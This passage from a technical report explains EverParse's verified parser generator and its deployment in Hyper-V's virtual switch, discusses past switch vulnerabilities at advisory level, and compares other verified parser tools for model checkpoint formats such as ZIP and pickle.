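An ordered-pair format, for example, has two 32-bit numbers, and the second must be at least as large as the first. Its type contains the pairs (fst, snd) with fst ≤ snd. Its parser maps eight bytes to such a pair or fails. Its validator returns either the position after the eighth byte or an error code.

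The main theorem is that, for every well-typed description t, as_validator(t) is a correct validator for as_parser(t), and as_parser(t) is a parser for values of as_type(t).

The proof is by induction on the structure of t. In F*, a function's type can state properties of its result, so the theorem is the type of as_validator. F* accepts the function's definition only if every case satisfies that type. For pairs, the function calls validate_pair on the validators for the two parts, and LowParse already contains the proof that the resulting validator is correct if those two are.

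The promises include the validator theorem, with one exception: an action can make the validator reject an input that p accepts.

The tests inside refinements are ordinary F* functions, so F* can check their arithmetic with its existing machinery. Otherwise, Swamy and colleagues would have had to build a separate safety checker.

### From an interpreter to plain C

As defined so far, as_validator is an interpreter. It goes through the description node by node and selects the validator each node needs. It would give correct results on real traffic, but slowly, because it would go through the same description again for every packet.

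Partial evaluation removes this overhead by doing all the work that depends only on known inputs in advance. For example, a function that computes x to the power n needs a loop. If n is always 3, a tool can run the loop ahead of time and keep only x × x × x. In the same way, partially evaluating an interpreter on a fixed program produces a compiled version of that program. Computer scientists call this the first Futamura projection, after a 1971 paper.

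To decide whether two types are equal, F* simplifies both as far as it can, even if they contain unknown variables. EverParse reuses this simplification on `as_validator(t)` for a given `t`. If `t` is a pair of 32-bit integers, F* first produces `validate_pair validate_u32 validate_u32`. It then replaces the combinators with their definitions until only simple code remains, which KaRaMeL can translate into C.

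F* simplifies (1 + 1) + y to 2 + y but leaves 1 + (1 + y) as it is, so Swamy and colleagues had to arrange their definitions carefully so that simplification would remove the whole interpreter. They also stop the simplification at the boundaries between named types, which makes each type definition its own C function. This keeps the code from growing too much and makes it easier to review. EverParse turned their 279-line TCP description into about 1,700 lines of C in 11 seconds on a laptop.

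### Reading the generated code

Ramananandro's slides show the C code for the ordered pair. With shorter names and simpler error handling, it amounts to this:

```c
uint64_t ValidateOrderedPair(uint8_t *in, uint64_t len, uint64_t start)
{
  if (len - start < 4) return Error(NOT_ENOUGH_DATA, start);
  uint64_t afterFst = start + 4;
  uint32_t fst = Load32Le(in + (uint32_t)start);

  if (len - afterFst < 4) return Error(NOT_ENOUGH_DATA, afterFst);
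  uint64_t afterSnd = afterFst + 4;
  uint32_t snd = Load32Le(in + (uint32_t)afterFst);

  if (fst > snd) return Error(CONSTRAINT_FAILED, afterSnd);
  return afterSnd;
}
```

The first line checks that at least four bytes remain by subtracting the position from the length. The subtraction cannot underflow because the position never exceeds the length. Once the check passes, adding 4 on the next line cannot overflow, since the sum is at most `len`. `Load32Le` reads four bytes as a little-endian number, with the least significant byte first.

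The code avoids double fetches by loading each number once into a local variable and comparing the local copies. Without the constraint, it wouldn't load the numbers at all, because any four bytes form a valid 32-bit integer and it would only need to check that the bytes exist.

The function reads 3 and 10 from the eight bytes 03 00 00 00 0A 00 00 00 and returns 8. It returns an error if the two numbers are swapped. The real code also calls an error handler with the type name, the field name and the reason for the error, first for the field that failed and then for each structure that contains it.

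The function ignores whatever follows the eighth byte. A description that must account for every byte of a file needs a final check. Project Everest's example for ELF, a common format for executable files, ends with an action that compares the parser's position with the file's size.

### Formats and properties outside 3D's reach

3D has no recursive types, so a type cannot contain itself and 3D cannot describe JSON, where a list may contain other lists. Swamy and colleagues had not needed recursion for network packets, and developers generally avoid it in Hyper-V's networking code because deep nesting can exhaust the stack. PulseParse handles some recursive formats, and the verified CBOR library EverCBOR relies on PulseParse, but Project Everest's reference for 3D still lists no recursive types.

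A 3D parser also only moves forward, so it cannot reread earlier bytes or try another interpretation if the first one fails. Offset fields can therefore only point ahead, and a file's tables must appear in the order the description lists them. The ELF example requires the first of the file's two tables to start immediately after the header. In *Access Control as Verified Parse Constraints*, Iammongkol, Huang and Eyers (2026) used 3D to decide which web requests a security gateway should let through. They had to leave out rules with wildcards, which they say would require backtracking.

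They also ran into a memory limit when they put all of a gateway's rules into one long constraint, which Z3 had to handle as a whole. Going from 8 rules to 16 raised Z3's peak memory from 1.3 to 7 GiB, and at 32 rules it ran out of memory with 24 GiB available. Splitting the rules into groups of eight solved the problem, and each group took about 17 seconds. Ordinary formats rarely need a constraint like this, since most fields depend on only a few others.

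3D does not generate serializers, although LowParse contains them. A program that writes the format needs separate serialization code, and no proof links that code to the parser.

The proofs about actions cover less than those about the format. EverParse proves that an action is memory safe, writes only where it is allowed to, and does not read the input twice. It does not prove that the action does what its author intended, so an action that stored a pointer to the wrong field would pass verification. If an action gives the application a pointer into the input, the application must also avoid reading those bytes twice.

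In one Hyper-V message, the actions check the format itself. The message contains two adjacent arrays, and each record in the first holds the number of its entries in the second and their starting position. The actions keep a running total of the entry counts, compare each starting position with the total so far, and then count down to zero over the second array. No theorem establishes that this code enforces the intended layout. Swamy and colleagues were considering a small logic for reasoning about actions, which would allow such a proof.

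Since their paper, the 3D language has gained the ability to follow memory addresses inside a message, which helps when a program passes a structure to the operating system's kernel. The application must supply a function that checks an address and gives the parser access to the data there, and the proofs assume that this function is safe. 3D can now also convert messages from 32-bit programs to the layout that a 64-bit kernel uses. Project Everest has proved that every message accepted after such a conversion is valid, but not yet that every valid message is accepted.

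People still have to audit a description against the written standard, even if a language model drafted it, as in *3DGen* (2024). To help, EverParse can translate a description into a formula and use Z3 to find byte strings that satisfy it and others that do not, which the author can inspect. Z3 can also search for an input that only one of two descriptions accepts. If it proves that there is none, the two descriptions accept exactly the same inputs.

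### Lengths and positions

The generated code stores positions as 64-bit numbers but converts them to 32 bits when it reads from memory. At position 4,294,967,300, it would read from position 4 instead. This cannot happen if the input is smaller than 4 GiB. The functions that applications are meant to call enforce that limit because their length parameter is a 32-bit number.

The 32-bit limit still applies, according to Project Everest's current reference. The length parameter has 32 bits, the size of every array must fit into 32 bits, and actions receive positions as 32-bit numbers. EverParse can generate a small program for testing a parser on files, but this program rejects any file larger than 4 GB, according to Project Everest's manual.

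Many checkpoints are larger. Eight billion two-byte weights take up 16 GB. If a C program passed 16,000,000,000 as the length, C would silently reduce it to 3,115,098,112. The validator would remain memory safe, but it would read at most the first 3.1 GB, and the caller could wrongly assume that it had checked the whole file.

Descriptions can work around this because 3D's constraints support 64-bit numbers. The ELF description receives the file's size as a 64-bit parameter. For each segment of the program, it checks that the segment's length is less than the file's size and that its offset is at most the file's size minus that length. This is the same range check as before, and the parser can do it without reading the segment. So an application could pass the validator only the header of a large file, along with the file's full size.

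EverParse can also generate validators that read from a stream instead of a buffer. The application then supplies functions that check whether n more bytes are available, read n bytes, and skip n bytes, where n is a 64-bit integer. The size of each array must still fit in 32 bits, and EverParse does not verify the functions the application supplies.

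## What happened when EverParse was deployed in Hyper-V and Windows?

Hyper-V is Microsoft's software for running virtual machines, and the company's cloud, Azure, runs on it. One physical machine, the host, runs several virtual machines, or guests, which may belong to different customers. When a guest sends packets over the network, its driver, NetVsc, passes them to the Virtual Switch, a component of the host's Windows kernel. The switch forwards them to the physical network card or to another guest.

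Anyone can rent a virtual machine and change the driver inside it, so the switch must safely handle malformed messages. *A Dive in to Hyper-V Architecture and Vulnerabilities* (Joly and Bialek, 2018) describes an attack in which a modified Linux driver sent a long string without the zero byte that should have ended it. When the switch logged the string in an error message, the switch read past the string's end. *Hardening Hyper-V Through Offensive Security Research* (Rabet, 2018) points out that the switch is not sandboxed, so an attacker who takes it over controls the host and every guest on it.

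In confidential computing, customers also want protection from the operator of the host, so NetVsc, which runs in the guest, has to check what the switch sends. Microsoft therefore put verified parsers in both the guest and the host.

The messages use four nested protocols. The outermost, NVSP, has 13 kinds of message that a guest can send to the host. One kind encloses an RNDIS message, which holds either an ordinary network packet or a numbered request to read or change a setting of the network adapter. Some of these requests carry structures from a fourth protocol, NDIS. The parsers check each layer only when the switch is about to use it, so handling a packet with a bad outer header takes very little time.

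### One pass over shared memory

Copying every packet from guest to host would be slow, so some packets stay in memory that both can access. A malicious guest can then change a packet while the host is checking it, so the switch needs parsers free of double fetches.

Even if the parser reads each byte at most once, the guest can change bytes that the parser has not yet read. Suppose a packet contains the bytes A and B, and the guest overwrites them with C and D just after the host reads A. The host then sees A followed by D, a packet that may never have existed in memory at any one moment. Swamy and colleagues point out that the guest gains nothing by this, because it could have sent A and D in the first place. The parser has to handle that packet correctly anyway, and the proofs cover it.

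The switch would lose this protection if the rest of its code read its data from the shared packet. For packets that carry network traffic, the parser therefore copies what the switch needs into the host's own memory during the same pass. These packets contain an array of extra information with 12 kinds of item, each with its own destination in the host's memory.

Deployment required a proof that the parsers never fetch a byte twice, according to the project's retrospective, *Project Everest* (2025). The researchers had to add it quickly to meet a product deadline. The proof also helped with speed, because some of the old code made a safe copy of a packet before checking it, which the new code could skip.

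### Recovering the formats

In 2018, Barry Bond, an engineer on the project, suggested using EverParse in Windows. The following year, the researchers and one of Microsoft's security teams reviewed past vulnerabilities to find where verified parsers would help most, and they started with Hyper-V's networking.

The engineers had to find out what the formats were before they could generate any parsers. Some formats were specified only by the behavior of the existing code, and some had accumulated proprietary extensions over many years. *Project Everest* calls this work "specification archaeology". A description that was too strict would cut off older guests that had always worked, but one that copied everything the old code accepted might preserve mistakes. To catch unintended changes, the engineers relied on differential testing, which compares how the old and new code treat the same messages.

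The engineers sometimes made the new description stricter than the original design. Each item of extra information in a packet has a field that specifies where its data begins, and the original design allowed unused bytes before the data. The engineers decided that this padding was wasteful in packets where speed matters, so the new description requires the data to start at byte 12, immediately after the item's header.

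The engineers also had to reorganize the guest's driver, because its code for handling incoming NVSP messages was scattered over several places. Bratus and colleagues call this pattern a shotgun parser, and a generated parser cannot replace it until the checks are gathered together. The engineers rearranged the driver so that messages arrived at two points, one for five kinds of data message and the other for seven kinds of completion message.

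3D could express nearly every format the team found. Only one message, the NDIS message with two adjacent arrays whose counts and positions must agree, needed hand-written actions to check its format. Putting each record next to its entries would have been simpler, but the NDIS standard required the two arrays. Elsewhere in the switch, actions only copied out data that the parser had already checked, so theorems cover all but a small part of the format checking.

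### Size, speed and maintenance

Swamy and colleagues count 137 structures, 22 casetypes and 30 enumerations in the finished descriptions, which total 5,026 lines of 3D. EverParse generated 22,393 lines of C and 1,057 lines of header files from them in 82 seconds on a laptop. An earlier version without partial evaluation took five minutes, according to Ramananandro's 2023 slides.

Accounts from 2025 give larger numbers. *Project Everest* reports about 30,000 lines of C from about 5,000 lines of 3D, while Ramananandro puts the descriptions at 6,000 lines. These figures are poor evidence that the deployment in the switch has grown, because Ramananandro had already given the figure of 30,000 in a 2021 blog post, before the paper with the lower count appeared. The round figures may also include descriptions of TCP, Ethernet and five other standard formats, which the paper lists but which Microsoft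 had not yet released in production code. These descriptions and their header files bring the totals to 5,845 lines of 3D and 29,496 lines of C.

The product team would accept the parsers only if they broke no existing functionality and added at most 2% to the processor cycles per byte. The parsers met both conditions, and in some configurations they were slightly faster than the code they replaced. Microsoft did not publish the measurements, so outsiders know only that the overhead stayed within 2%. The result is still somewhat credible because the product team set the limit and had no reason to favor verified code.

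Verification also saved work. Omar Cardona, who led the engineering of the networking software, said that the team could not have handled so many complex messages by hand in the time available. Microsoft added EverParse and its proof tools to the Windows build system, so product teams can edit a description and regenerate the C code themselves. When engineers reorganized descriptions without meaning to change the format, they proved in F* that the old and new versions were equivalent. By mid-2025, nobody had patched the generated C directly, although the team had kept it readable partly to allow emergency patches.

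EverParse has since spread beyond the switch. Ramananandro lists its use in three other areas of Windows networking and in eBPF for Windows, a system for running small add-on programs inside the kernel. There, EverParse handles the ELF files that contain these programs. *Project Everest* reports that Microsoft products now also use 3D for file formats and for data structures full of pointers. Neither source gives figures for these newer uses, so the switch remains the only deployment whose scale is public.

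### Microsoft's security tests

A security team independent of the researchers and the networking engineers examined the new code before its release. It audited the descriptions, wrote its own tests and studied past and open bugs in the switch. Swamy and colleagues report that the parsers closed, or would have closed, the bugs they were meant to address, but do not say how many such bugs there were or what share of all the switch's bugs they made up. That share would be the most useful number for anyone deciding whether to use such parsers elsewhere.

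Fuzzing found no bugs in the parsers, and neither did several days of running SAGE, a fuzzer that analyzes a program's branches and uses a solver to find inputs that reach each one. The proofs would lead one to expect this, so the fuzzing mainly checks their assumptions, such as a correct translation from F* to C. It is a weak test of whether the descriptions are right, since a parser that rejects a legitimate message does not crash.

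Once the verified parsers were in place, several of Microsoft's fuzzers stopped working effectively, because the parsers rejected nearly all the malformed messages that the fuzzers sent to the switch. This is good evidence that the parsers work, but it also meant that the fuzzers no longer tested the hand-written code behind the parsers, where any remaining bugs were more likely to be. The researchers began helping the fuzzing teams generate well-formed messages from the 3D descriptions so that the tests could reach that code again.

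*Project Everest*, a retrospective by the parsers' developers, states that the parsers had run in production for five years "without incident", but it does not define an incident. The developers had found 26 bugs in F* that could let it accept a false proof, three of which were still open in June 2025. They had also found six bugs in KaRaMeL that its internal checks and the C compiler had missed. In one of these, 8-bit arithmetic that should have wrapped around to 0 gave 128 in the generated C. EverParse rejects arithmetic that can overflow, so a format description could not have depended on that calculation, but a different translation bug could still have produced incorrect C from correctly proved code.

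Independent tests add little evidence. *Fuzzer-V* (Ben-Porath, 2023) reports that the security company CyberArk fuzzed one of Hyper-V's host drivers on Windows 11 and found no new vulnerabilities. It does not name the driver, so the test may not have touched the virtual switch. CyberArk also ran only one instance of the fuzzer, and any crash would have brought down the physical machine.

### Later vulnerabilities in the virtual switch

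In May 2021, Microsoft patched a flaw in the virtual switch, CVE-2021-28476, with a severity of 9.9 out of 10. Harpaz and Hadar (2021), who found it by fuzzing, explain it in *Critical 9.9 Vulnerability in Hyper-V Allowed Attackers to Exploit Azure*. Inside the host, the switch sometimes wraps one adapter request in another, and the outer request contains a pointer to the inner one. Guests have no reason to send wrapped requests, but the switch accepted them. Its tracing code, which records requests for debugging, followed the guest's pointer without checking it.

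A guest could therefore choose the address that the host's kernel would read. An invalid address crashed the host and all its virtual machines. Harpaz and Hadar also describe a harder attack, in which the address belongs to a hardware device and reading it triggers side effects that let the attacker run code on the host.

It is unclear whether the affected versions of Windows contained EverParse's parsers. The flaw first appeared in a build from August 2019, around the time the researchers started working with the networking engineers. In his 2021 blog post, Ramananandro wrote that the hardened networking was available through the Windows Insider Program, which distributes test versions, and that future versions of Windows Server would include it. The flaw affected Windows 7 to 10 and Windows Server 2008 to 2019, which suggests that those versions lacked the new parsers. But Ramananandro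 wrote in later slides that EverParse had been used in Windows and Azure since 2019 and that Microsoft had also added the parsers to older versions. Neither Harpaz and Hadar nor the European Union's advisory, *Critical Vulnerability in Microsoft Hyper-V* (CERT-EU, 2021), mentions EverParse.

Harpaz and Hadar follow the function calls from the general message handler to a function that only logs wrapped requests. The bad read happened in that function, which used a message after the switch had accepted it, so it was not a failure of a verified parser.

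A verified parser in front of that code might still have prevented the attack if whoever wrote the description had known that guests never legitimately send the wrapped request, and had left it out. The parser would then have rejected the request because it matched no case. If the description had allowed the request, the parser would have accepted any number as the pointer, and the tracing code would have followed it as before.

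In an older flaw, CVE-2019-0717, correct checks failed to protect the code that ran after them. The flaw involved a message that gives the position and length of a parameter's name. As Esage (2021) explains in *Microsoft Hyper-V Virtual Network Switch VmsMpCommonPvtSetRequestCommon Out of Bounds Read*, four checks correctly confirmed that the data lay inside the message. The switch then compared the name with an expected one and always read 28 bytes, even if the guest's name was shorter. If a short name sat at the end of a block of memory, the host could crash. A verified parser that enforced the same four checks would also have accepted this message. To stop the attack, the format description would have had to require a name of at least 28 bytes, or the comparison would have had to use the checked length.

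CERT.dk's *CVE-2024-43625* (2024) records another vulnerability in the switch, published in November 2024, after the verified parsers had become a standard part of Windows. It has a severity of 8.1 and could give an attacker higher privileges. Enginsight's *CVE-2024-43625* lists Windows 11 from version 22H2 onward and Windows Server 2022 among the affected systems. Swamy and colleagues had reported the hardened networking in Windows 11 two years earlier, so the parsers were presumably present.

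The cause was a use after free, meaning that the program kept using memory after releasing it. EverParse's validators allocate no heap memory, so the mistake was probably in the surrounding code, such as code that released a message too early. However, these records do not identify the faulty function, so they do not rule out that the verified parsers played a part.

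## Which other verified parser tools exist, and which suit files?

Model files are harder to parse than the messages that reach Hyper-V's virtual switch, which are short and can be read from front to back. A model file's metadata may contain lists inside lists, its header gives the positions of tensors (the arrays that hold the weights) further on in the file, and its sizes often need more than 32 bits. Programs also have to write these files, so a serializer matters as well as a parser. EverParse's 3D language falls short on each of these points. Other tools do better on some, but none does well on all.

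### Nested data and a counter

EverCBOR handles nested data in CBOR, a binary format similar to JSON. Ramananandro and colleagues built the library with PulseParse. It validates, parses and serializes CBOR in C or Rust, with proofs of memory safety, functional correctness and non-malleability.

The first three bits of a CBOR item give its type. The next five hold a small number, or indicate how many of the following bytes hold a larger one. For an array, this number is the element count. The nested list [1, [2, 3]] becomes the five bytes 82 01 82 02 03, where each 82 starts an array of two items.

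To keep stack use fixed, EverCBOR's validator uses a loop instead of calling itself for each inner list. A counter tracks how many items it still expects, starting at 1. At each item, the validator subtracts 1 and adds the number of that item's children. In the example, the counter goes to 2, 1, 2, 1 and 0, at which point the list is complete. Each item takes up at least one byte, so a header with an item count larger than the number of bytes left cannot be valid. The validator relies on this to keep the counter from overflowing.

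The method works for any format in which each item is a header followed only by its children, and the header alone determines the number of children. JSON meets neither condition, because a list ends with a closing bracket and its opening bracket doesn't specify the number of elements.

Ramananandro and colleagues proved that the loop accepts exactly the inputs that a recursive specification accepts. They did not formally prove the limit on stack use, because their logic cannot express it. Instead, they support the limit by arguing that the code contains no recursive functions, which is easy to check by reading it.

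CBOR's maps, which pair keys with values, cause more trouble. If a key occurs twice, two programs may pick different values for it. Keys can themselves be maps with their entries in any order, and comparing two such keys takes stack space that grows with the nesting. EverCBOR avoids these problems by accepting only the standard's deterministic encoding, in which integers take their shortest form and map entries are sorted by their keys' bytes. Equal keys then have equal bytes, so the validator only has to check that each key sorts after the previous one.

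However, EverCBOR rejects valid CBOR from programs that don't follow these rules. Project Everest describes support for the full format as work in progress. EverCBOR also lacks floating-point numbers, so a setting such as 0.7 would have to be stored as text or a scaled integer. Weights are less of a problem because a tensor can be stored as a byte string, whose contents the library doesn't interpret. The string's length can be a 64-bit number, and the generated C functions accept buffer lengths up to the machine's full word size, so 3D's 4 GiB limit doesn't apply.

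### Schemas for CBOR, and measured speed

Most programs expect particular fields, not just any valid CBOR. CDDL is a schema language for describing them. A schema for a tensor might look like this:

```
{ "name": tstr, "shape": [* uint], "data": bstr }
```

The schema describes a map with a text string, a list of unsigned integers and a byte string. EverCDDL turns such a schema into C or Rust types with a verified parser and serializer.

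EverCDDL first checks that the schema is unambiguous. For example, it rejects a choice between an unsigned integer and "any", which CDDL allows, because the alternatives overlap. A program could write 42 as "any", and the parser would read it back as an unsigned integer. EverCDDL also rejects recursive schemas, whose parsers would need more stack for deeper input.

Unlike 3D, CDDL cannot relate one field to another, so the schema cannot require the length of `data` to equal the product of the numbers in `shape` multiplied by the size of one weight. An application that used EverCDDL for tensors would have to check this in its own code, which EverCDDL's proof would not cover.

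Ramananandro and colleagues compared the generated C with two unverified CBOR libraries, QCBOR and TinyCBOR:

| Task | EverCDDL | QCBOR | TinyCBOR |
|---|---|---|---|
| Validate and parse a record of 8 integers | 3.33 µs | 1.91 µs | 3.78 µs |
| Serialize that record | 0.57 µs | 0.23 µs | 0.29 µs |
| Look up a key in a map of 8,000 entries | 138 µs | 282 µs | 306 µs |
| Validate 100 million integers in nested arrays | 2.67 s | 2.92 s | 2.68 s |
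| Read those integers after validation | 4.92 s | 2.91 s | 2.68 s |
| Serialize those integers | 2.06 s | 0.75 s | 1.23 s |

Lookups are fast because validation has already established that the keys are in order, so the search can stop early and compare raw bytes. Reading nested arrays is slow because the code goes through each inner array twice, once to read it and once to find where the next one begins. Serialization includes a wasteful size check for every integer, and replacing it by hand with a constant made the code 20% faster. Better engineering could fix both problems without weakening the proofs.

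The nested arrays filled about 100 MB, so validation ran at roughly 37 MB per second. At that rate, a 16 GB checkpoint would take about seven minutes, with or without proofs. But this test used one-byte items, each with its own header. A file that stored each tensor as a byte string would have only a few hundred or a few thousand headers to check.

PulseParse could describe formats other than CBOR, but it has no simple language for doing so. Iammongkol and colleagues point out that users would have to write specifications in Pulse, the part of F* that supports separation logic, and do some proofs by hand. They chose 3D for their gateway so that people writing security policies would not have to do this work.

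### Vest

Vest generates Rust. Cai, Singh and colleagues (2025), in *Vest*, present it as a tool for programmers with no training in formal proof. In its description language, the format that stores "Ada" as a length and three letters would look like this:

```
name = {
  @len: u8,
  letters: [u8; @len],
}
```

The @ sign marks a field that later fields may refer to. Vest turns the description into a Rust data type and functions that parse it, serialize it and calculate its serialized length.

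Like EverParse, Vest builds these functions from a library of verified combinators. According to conference slides by Cai and colleagues, the library has 10 basic combinators and 9 that combine others. Each one contains its specification, parser, serializer and the proofs that connect them, so combining two formats also combines their proofs. Verus, a verifier for Rust programs, then checks the generated code for each new format, and verification fails if the code disagrees with the specification. Verus would not detect an error in how the generator translated a format description into a specification, so people still have to trust that translation or inspect the specification.

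The project's documentation, Secure Foundations' *Vest*, lists the proved properties, which include, under other names, the round trips in both directions, non-malleability and the prefix property. The generated code also terminates on every input and never panics, which addresses Ramananandro's objection that ordinary Rust parsers may stop a program at runtime. Cai and colleagues add resistance to basic timing attacks, which EverParse does not offer. This resistance matters more for cryptographic messages than for model files.

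Cai and colleagues compared the speed of Vest's parsers and serializers with that of hand-written, unverified Rust libraries on three formats. They used 1,000 Bitcoin blocks (about 670 MB in all), recorded TLS handshakes with 100 popular websites, and 30 C programs compiled to WebAssembly, a portable format for executable code. They report that Vest's parsers and serializers were at least as fast as the hand-written ones. This is encouraging for model files because the WebAssembly test used real files and compared Vest with a mature library, wasmparser.

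The Vest paper also reports that verification is orders of magnitude faster than in comparable earlier work. Vest's output verifies within seconds, while EverParse's takes several hours. That comparison uses the EverParse of 2019, so it is weak evidence of how Vest compares with 3D, which is much faster.

Vest suits large files better than 3D does. The library reference by Secure Foundations includes 64-bit integers and byte fields whose length is determined at runtime, and Rust's buffer lengths have 64 bits on a 64-bit machine. But the developers say Vest is at an early stage. According to their slides, they are still working on recursive formats, formats full of pointers, and parsers that do not read straight through the input. Two other verified projects use Vest, one to check website certificates and one to compile security protocols, but neither reads large files.

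### RecordFlux, Narcissus and ASN.1

AdaCore's RecordFlux generates parsers and serializers for binary messages. The generated code is in SPARK, a subset of the Ada language that is designed for proof. SPARK's tools prove that this code has no runtime errors, such as reads outside an array or integer overflows. RecordFlux is a practical choice for embedded devices, but a C++ or Python project would have to add an Ada compiler to its build.

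Narcissus, a library for the proof assistant Coq, defines a format as a relation between values and byte strings, which lets one value have several valid encodings. EverParse instead treats the parser itself as the definition of the format. Narcissus derives an encoder and a decoder from the relation and proves both correct with respect to it. Ramananandro and colleagues note that Narcissus produces functional OCaml programs instead of low-level code that works directly on the input buffer, and that it does not prove non-malleability. That property would be false anyway for a format that deliberately allows several encodings of one value.

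Researchers have also verified parsers for ASN.1, the older message standard that LangSec researchers criticized. ASN1* used EverParse's specification combinators to prove that DER, the encoding used in website certificates, is non-malleable. ARMOR produced a verified Haskell program that checks certificate chains.

*VUPER* (Zhou, Tu and colleagues, 2026) handles a more compact ASN.1 encoding that mobile networks use. The encoding packs fields without regard to byte boundaries, so a number from 1 to 8 takes only three bits. Newer phones and base stations may add fields that older ones skip. If an older device parses such a message and serializes the result, the new fields disappear and the output differs from the input, so non-malleability cannot hold. VUPER sets a flag when it skips unknown fields and guarantees a unique encoding only if the flag is unset. Otherwise, it guarantees that the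 serializer can write the parsed value in some valid form. File formats that gain fields over the years could use the same compromise.

VUPER's parser runs in OCaml and is about four times slower than C libraries. Zhou and colleagues intend it mainly as a reference for testing other parsers. They compared it with 11 parsers, four of them commercial, and found 20 kinds of inconsistency, which they used to carry out four attacks on two widely used open-source network programs. Testing existing parsers against a verified one takes less work than replacing a loader. A slow verified parser for model files could check the fast ones during testing without running in a product.

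### Files that a program cannot read in order

A ZIP archive keeps its table of contents at the end, and each entry points back to a stored file. A loader has to read the end first and then jump backward. None of the verified generators described so far has a notation for this.

Interval parsing grammars do. Zhang, Morrisett and Tan introduced them in 2023. Each rule in such a grammar states which range of the input it applies to, and the range can depend on values that earlier rules have read. For example:

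```
File -> Header[0, 8] Table[Header.offset, Header.offset + Header.size]
```

The header occupies bytes 0 to 7 and contains two numbers, an offset and a size. If the offset is 20 and the size is 64, the rule for the table can read only bytes 20 to 83. In a 100-byte file, an offset of 60 with the same size would make the range end at 124, so parsing would fail. Every jump includes this range check automatically, so the author cannot forget it.

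Jumps can also make a parser loop forever, a danger that sequential parsers don't have. This would happen if a record contained its own position as the position of the next record. The designers therefore developed a check for cycles of rules in which the range might not shrink. They also wrote a generator that turns a grammar into a parser, and grammars for ZIP, ELF, GIF and part of PDF.

Their theory defines what a grammar means and when parsing terminates, but their generator has no machine-checked proof that its output follows the grammar. This matters because the sum in the example can overflow in a program, though not in the grammar. A proof like EverParse's would rule out that overflow.

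Daedalus, a description language from the company Galois, treats the input stream as a value that a parser can store, shorten or replace. To follow an offset, a parser creates a stream that starts at the required position and continues parsing there. Ramananandro and colleagues report large-scale use of Daedalus, including for PDF. Daedalus generates parsers in Haskell and C++, but it does not generate serializers. The C++ code is meant to be memory safe, but no formal proof shows that it is.

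Many model files don't need all the features of these languages. A tensor's bytes are numbers with no further structure, so a parser doesn't have to jump to them. It only has to check that the range given in the header lies inside the file, as 3D's description of ELF files does for program segments. A parser does have to jump when an offset points to data that needs parsing too, as in ZIP.

| Tool | Output | Serializer | Machine-checked proof | Main obstacle for model files |
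|---|---|---|---|---|
| EverParse 3D | C | no | correctness and safety | 32-bit lengths, no recursion, forward reading only |
| EverCBOR, EverCDDL | C, Rust | yes | correctness and safety | CBOR only, no floating-point numbers |
| Vest | Rust | yes | correctness and safety | no recursion or jumps yet |
| RecordFlux | SPARK | yes | no runtime errors | designed for messages, needs Ada |
| Narcissus | OCaml | yes | correctness | no low-level code |
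| VUPER | OCaml | yes | correctness | one ASN.1 encoding, slower than C |
| Interval parsing grammars | generated parser | no | none for generated code | research prototype |
| Daedalus | Haskell, C++ | no | none | no proof of memory safety |

EverCBOR is the most complete choice for a new checkpoint format because it has a serializer, supports 64-bit lengths and handles nested data safely. If the project can use Rust, Vest looks more promising than 3D for an existing binary format with a flat header, because Vest supports 64-bit lengths and has a serializer.

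### JSON, Protocol Buffers and ZIP

AI software mostly stores its structured data in JSON, Protocol Buffers or ZIP, and verified tools cover all three poorly.

For JSON, the closest results are general parsers for text grammars. Ramananandro and colleagues mention two by Lasser and colleagues, from 2019 and 2021, both verified in Coq. Given a grammar, such a parser returns a syntax tree exactly when the grammar allows the text. JSON's grammar is small, so this part of the problem is essentially solved. However, the proofs do not cover splitting characters into tokens or converting decimal text such as 0.1 into binary numbers. The JSON grammar also permits duplicate keys in an object, which a loader should reject.

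EverParse's combinators require non-malleability, meaning that each value has only one encoding. They do not fit JSON directly because JSON allows any amount of space between tokens. EverCBOR's developers faced a similar problem because CBOR can store the same integer in several lengths. They first defined a "raw" value that records the encoded length of every integer and the order of entries in every map, which makes the encoding unique, and then added the stricter rules on top. A JSON parser could record the spaces in the same way. Another option is a verified preprocessor that turns text into a binary form. Iammongkol and colleagues placed one in front of EverParse to handle web requests. Either approach would take substantial work, which is one reason to consider proofs about an existing C library such as cJSON.

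In 2019, Ye and Delaware used Narcissus to build a verified compiler for Protocol Buffers. It turns a message description into an encoder and a decoder, with a proof that encoding and then decoding any valid message returns the original. Narcissus's relations suit this format because a sender may put fields in any order and write the number 5 as 05 or as 85 00. But the compiler supports only a subset of the format, and the functional code it produces is not a replacement for Google's C++ library. A faster verified version would also need a rule for unknown fields, which receivers skip, much as VUPER does. Large sizes are less of a concern because Google limits a message to 2 GiB.

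ZIP matters because PyTorch saves its checkpoints as ZIP archives. Some tools, including lean-zip, have verified code for the compression inside an archive, but lean-zip's archive reader is unproved. An interval parsing grammar for ZIP describes the archive format but doesn't prove the code correct. A proof would also need an agreed definition of a valid archive. *My ZIP isn't your ZIP* (You, Chen and colleagues, 2025) attributes differences between parsers to ZIP's imprecise specification, and uses a fuzzer called ZipDiff to search for them. An archive records each file's name and size both before the file's data and in a table at the end, and a parser may trust either copy.

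A verified parser for general ZIP archives would have to choose among these interpretations and would then disagree with some existing software. A checkpoint loader could instead reject any archive whose two copies differ or whose stored files have gaps or overlaps between them. The scanner that checks a checkpoint for malicious content would have to apply the same rules, or an attacker could still craft an archive that the two programs read differently.

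## Can a verified parser make pickle checkpoints safe?

A verified ZIP reader would only extract the files inside a PyTorch checkpoint. One of those files, data.pkl, is a pickle, which is a program. According to PyTorch's *Serialization semantics*, it describes how to build tensors and dictionaries from the raw numbers stored in the archive's numbered entries.

### The pickle machine

Comments in Python's source code describe the virtual machine that runs pickles. It has a stack, which holds the objects it is working on, and a memo, a numbered store for objects that will be used again. The machine runs each instruction, called an opcode, once and in order until it reaches STOP, then returns the object on top of the stack. It has no loops, conditions or arithmetic.

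One example in the comments is a list that contains the dictionary {b'abc': 'def'}, where the b marks raw bytes as opposed to text. These are the opcodes for the dictionary alone, without those that write to the memo and with a STOP at the end:

| Opcode | Stack afterwards |
|---|---|
| EMPTY_DICT | {} |
| GLOBAL '_codecs encode' | {}, function encode |
| MARK | {}, function encode, mark |
| BINUNICODE 'abc' | {}, function encode, mark, 'abc' |
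| BINUNICODE 'latin1' | {}, function encode, mark, 'abc', 'latin1' |
| TUPLE | {}, function encode, ('abc', 'latin1') |
| REDUCE | {}, b'abc' |
| BINUNICODE 'def' | {}, b'abc', 'def' |
| SETITEM | {b'abc': 'def'} |
| STOP | (the machine returns the dictionary) |

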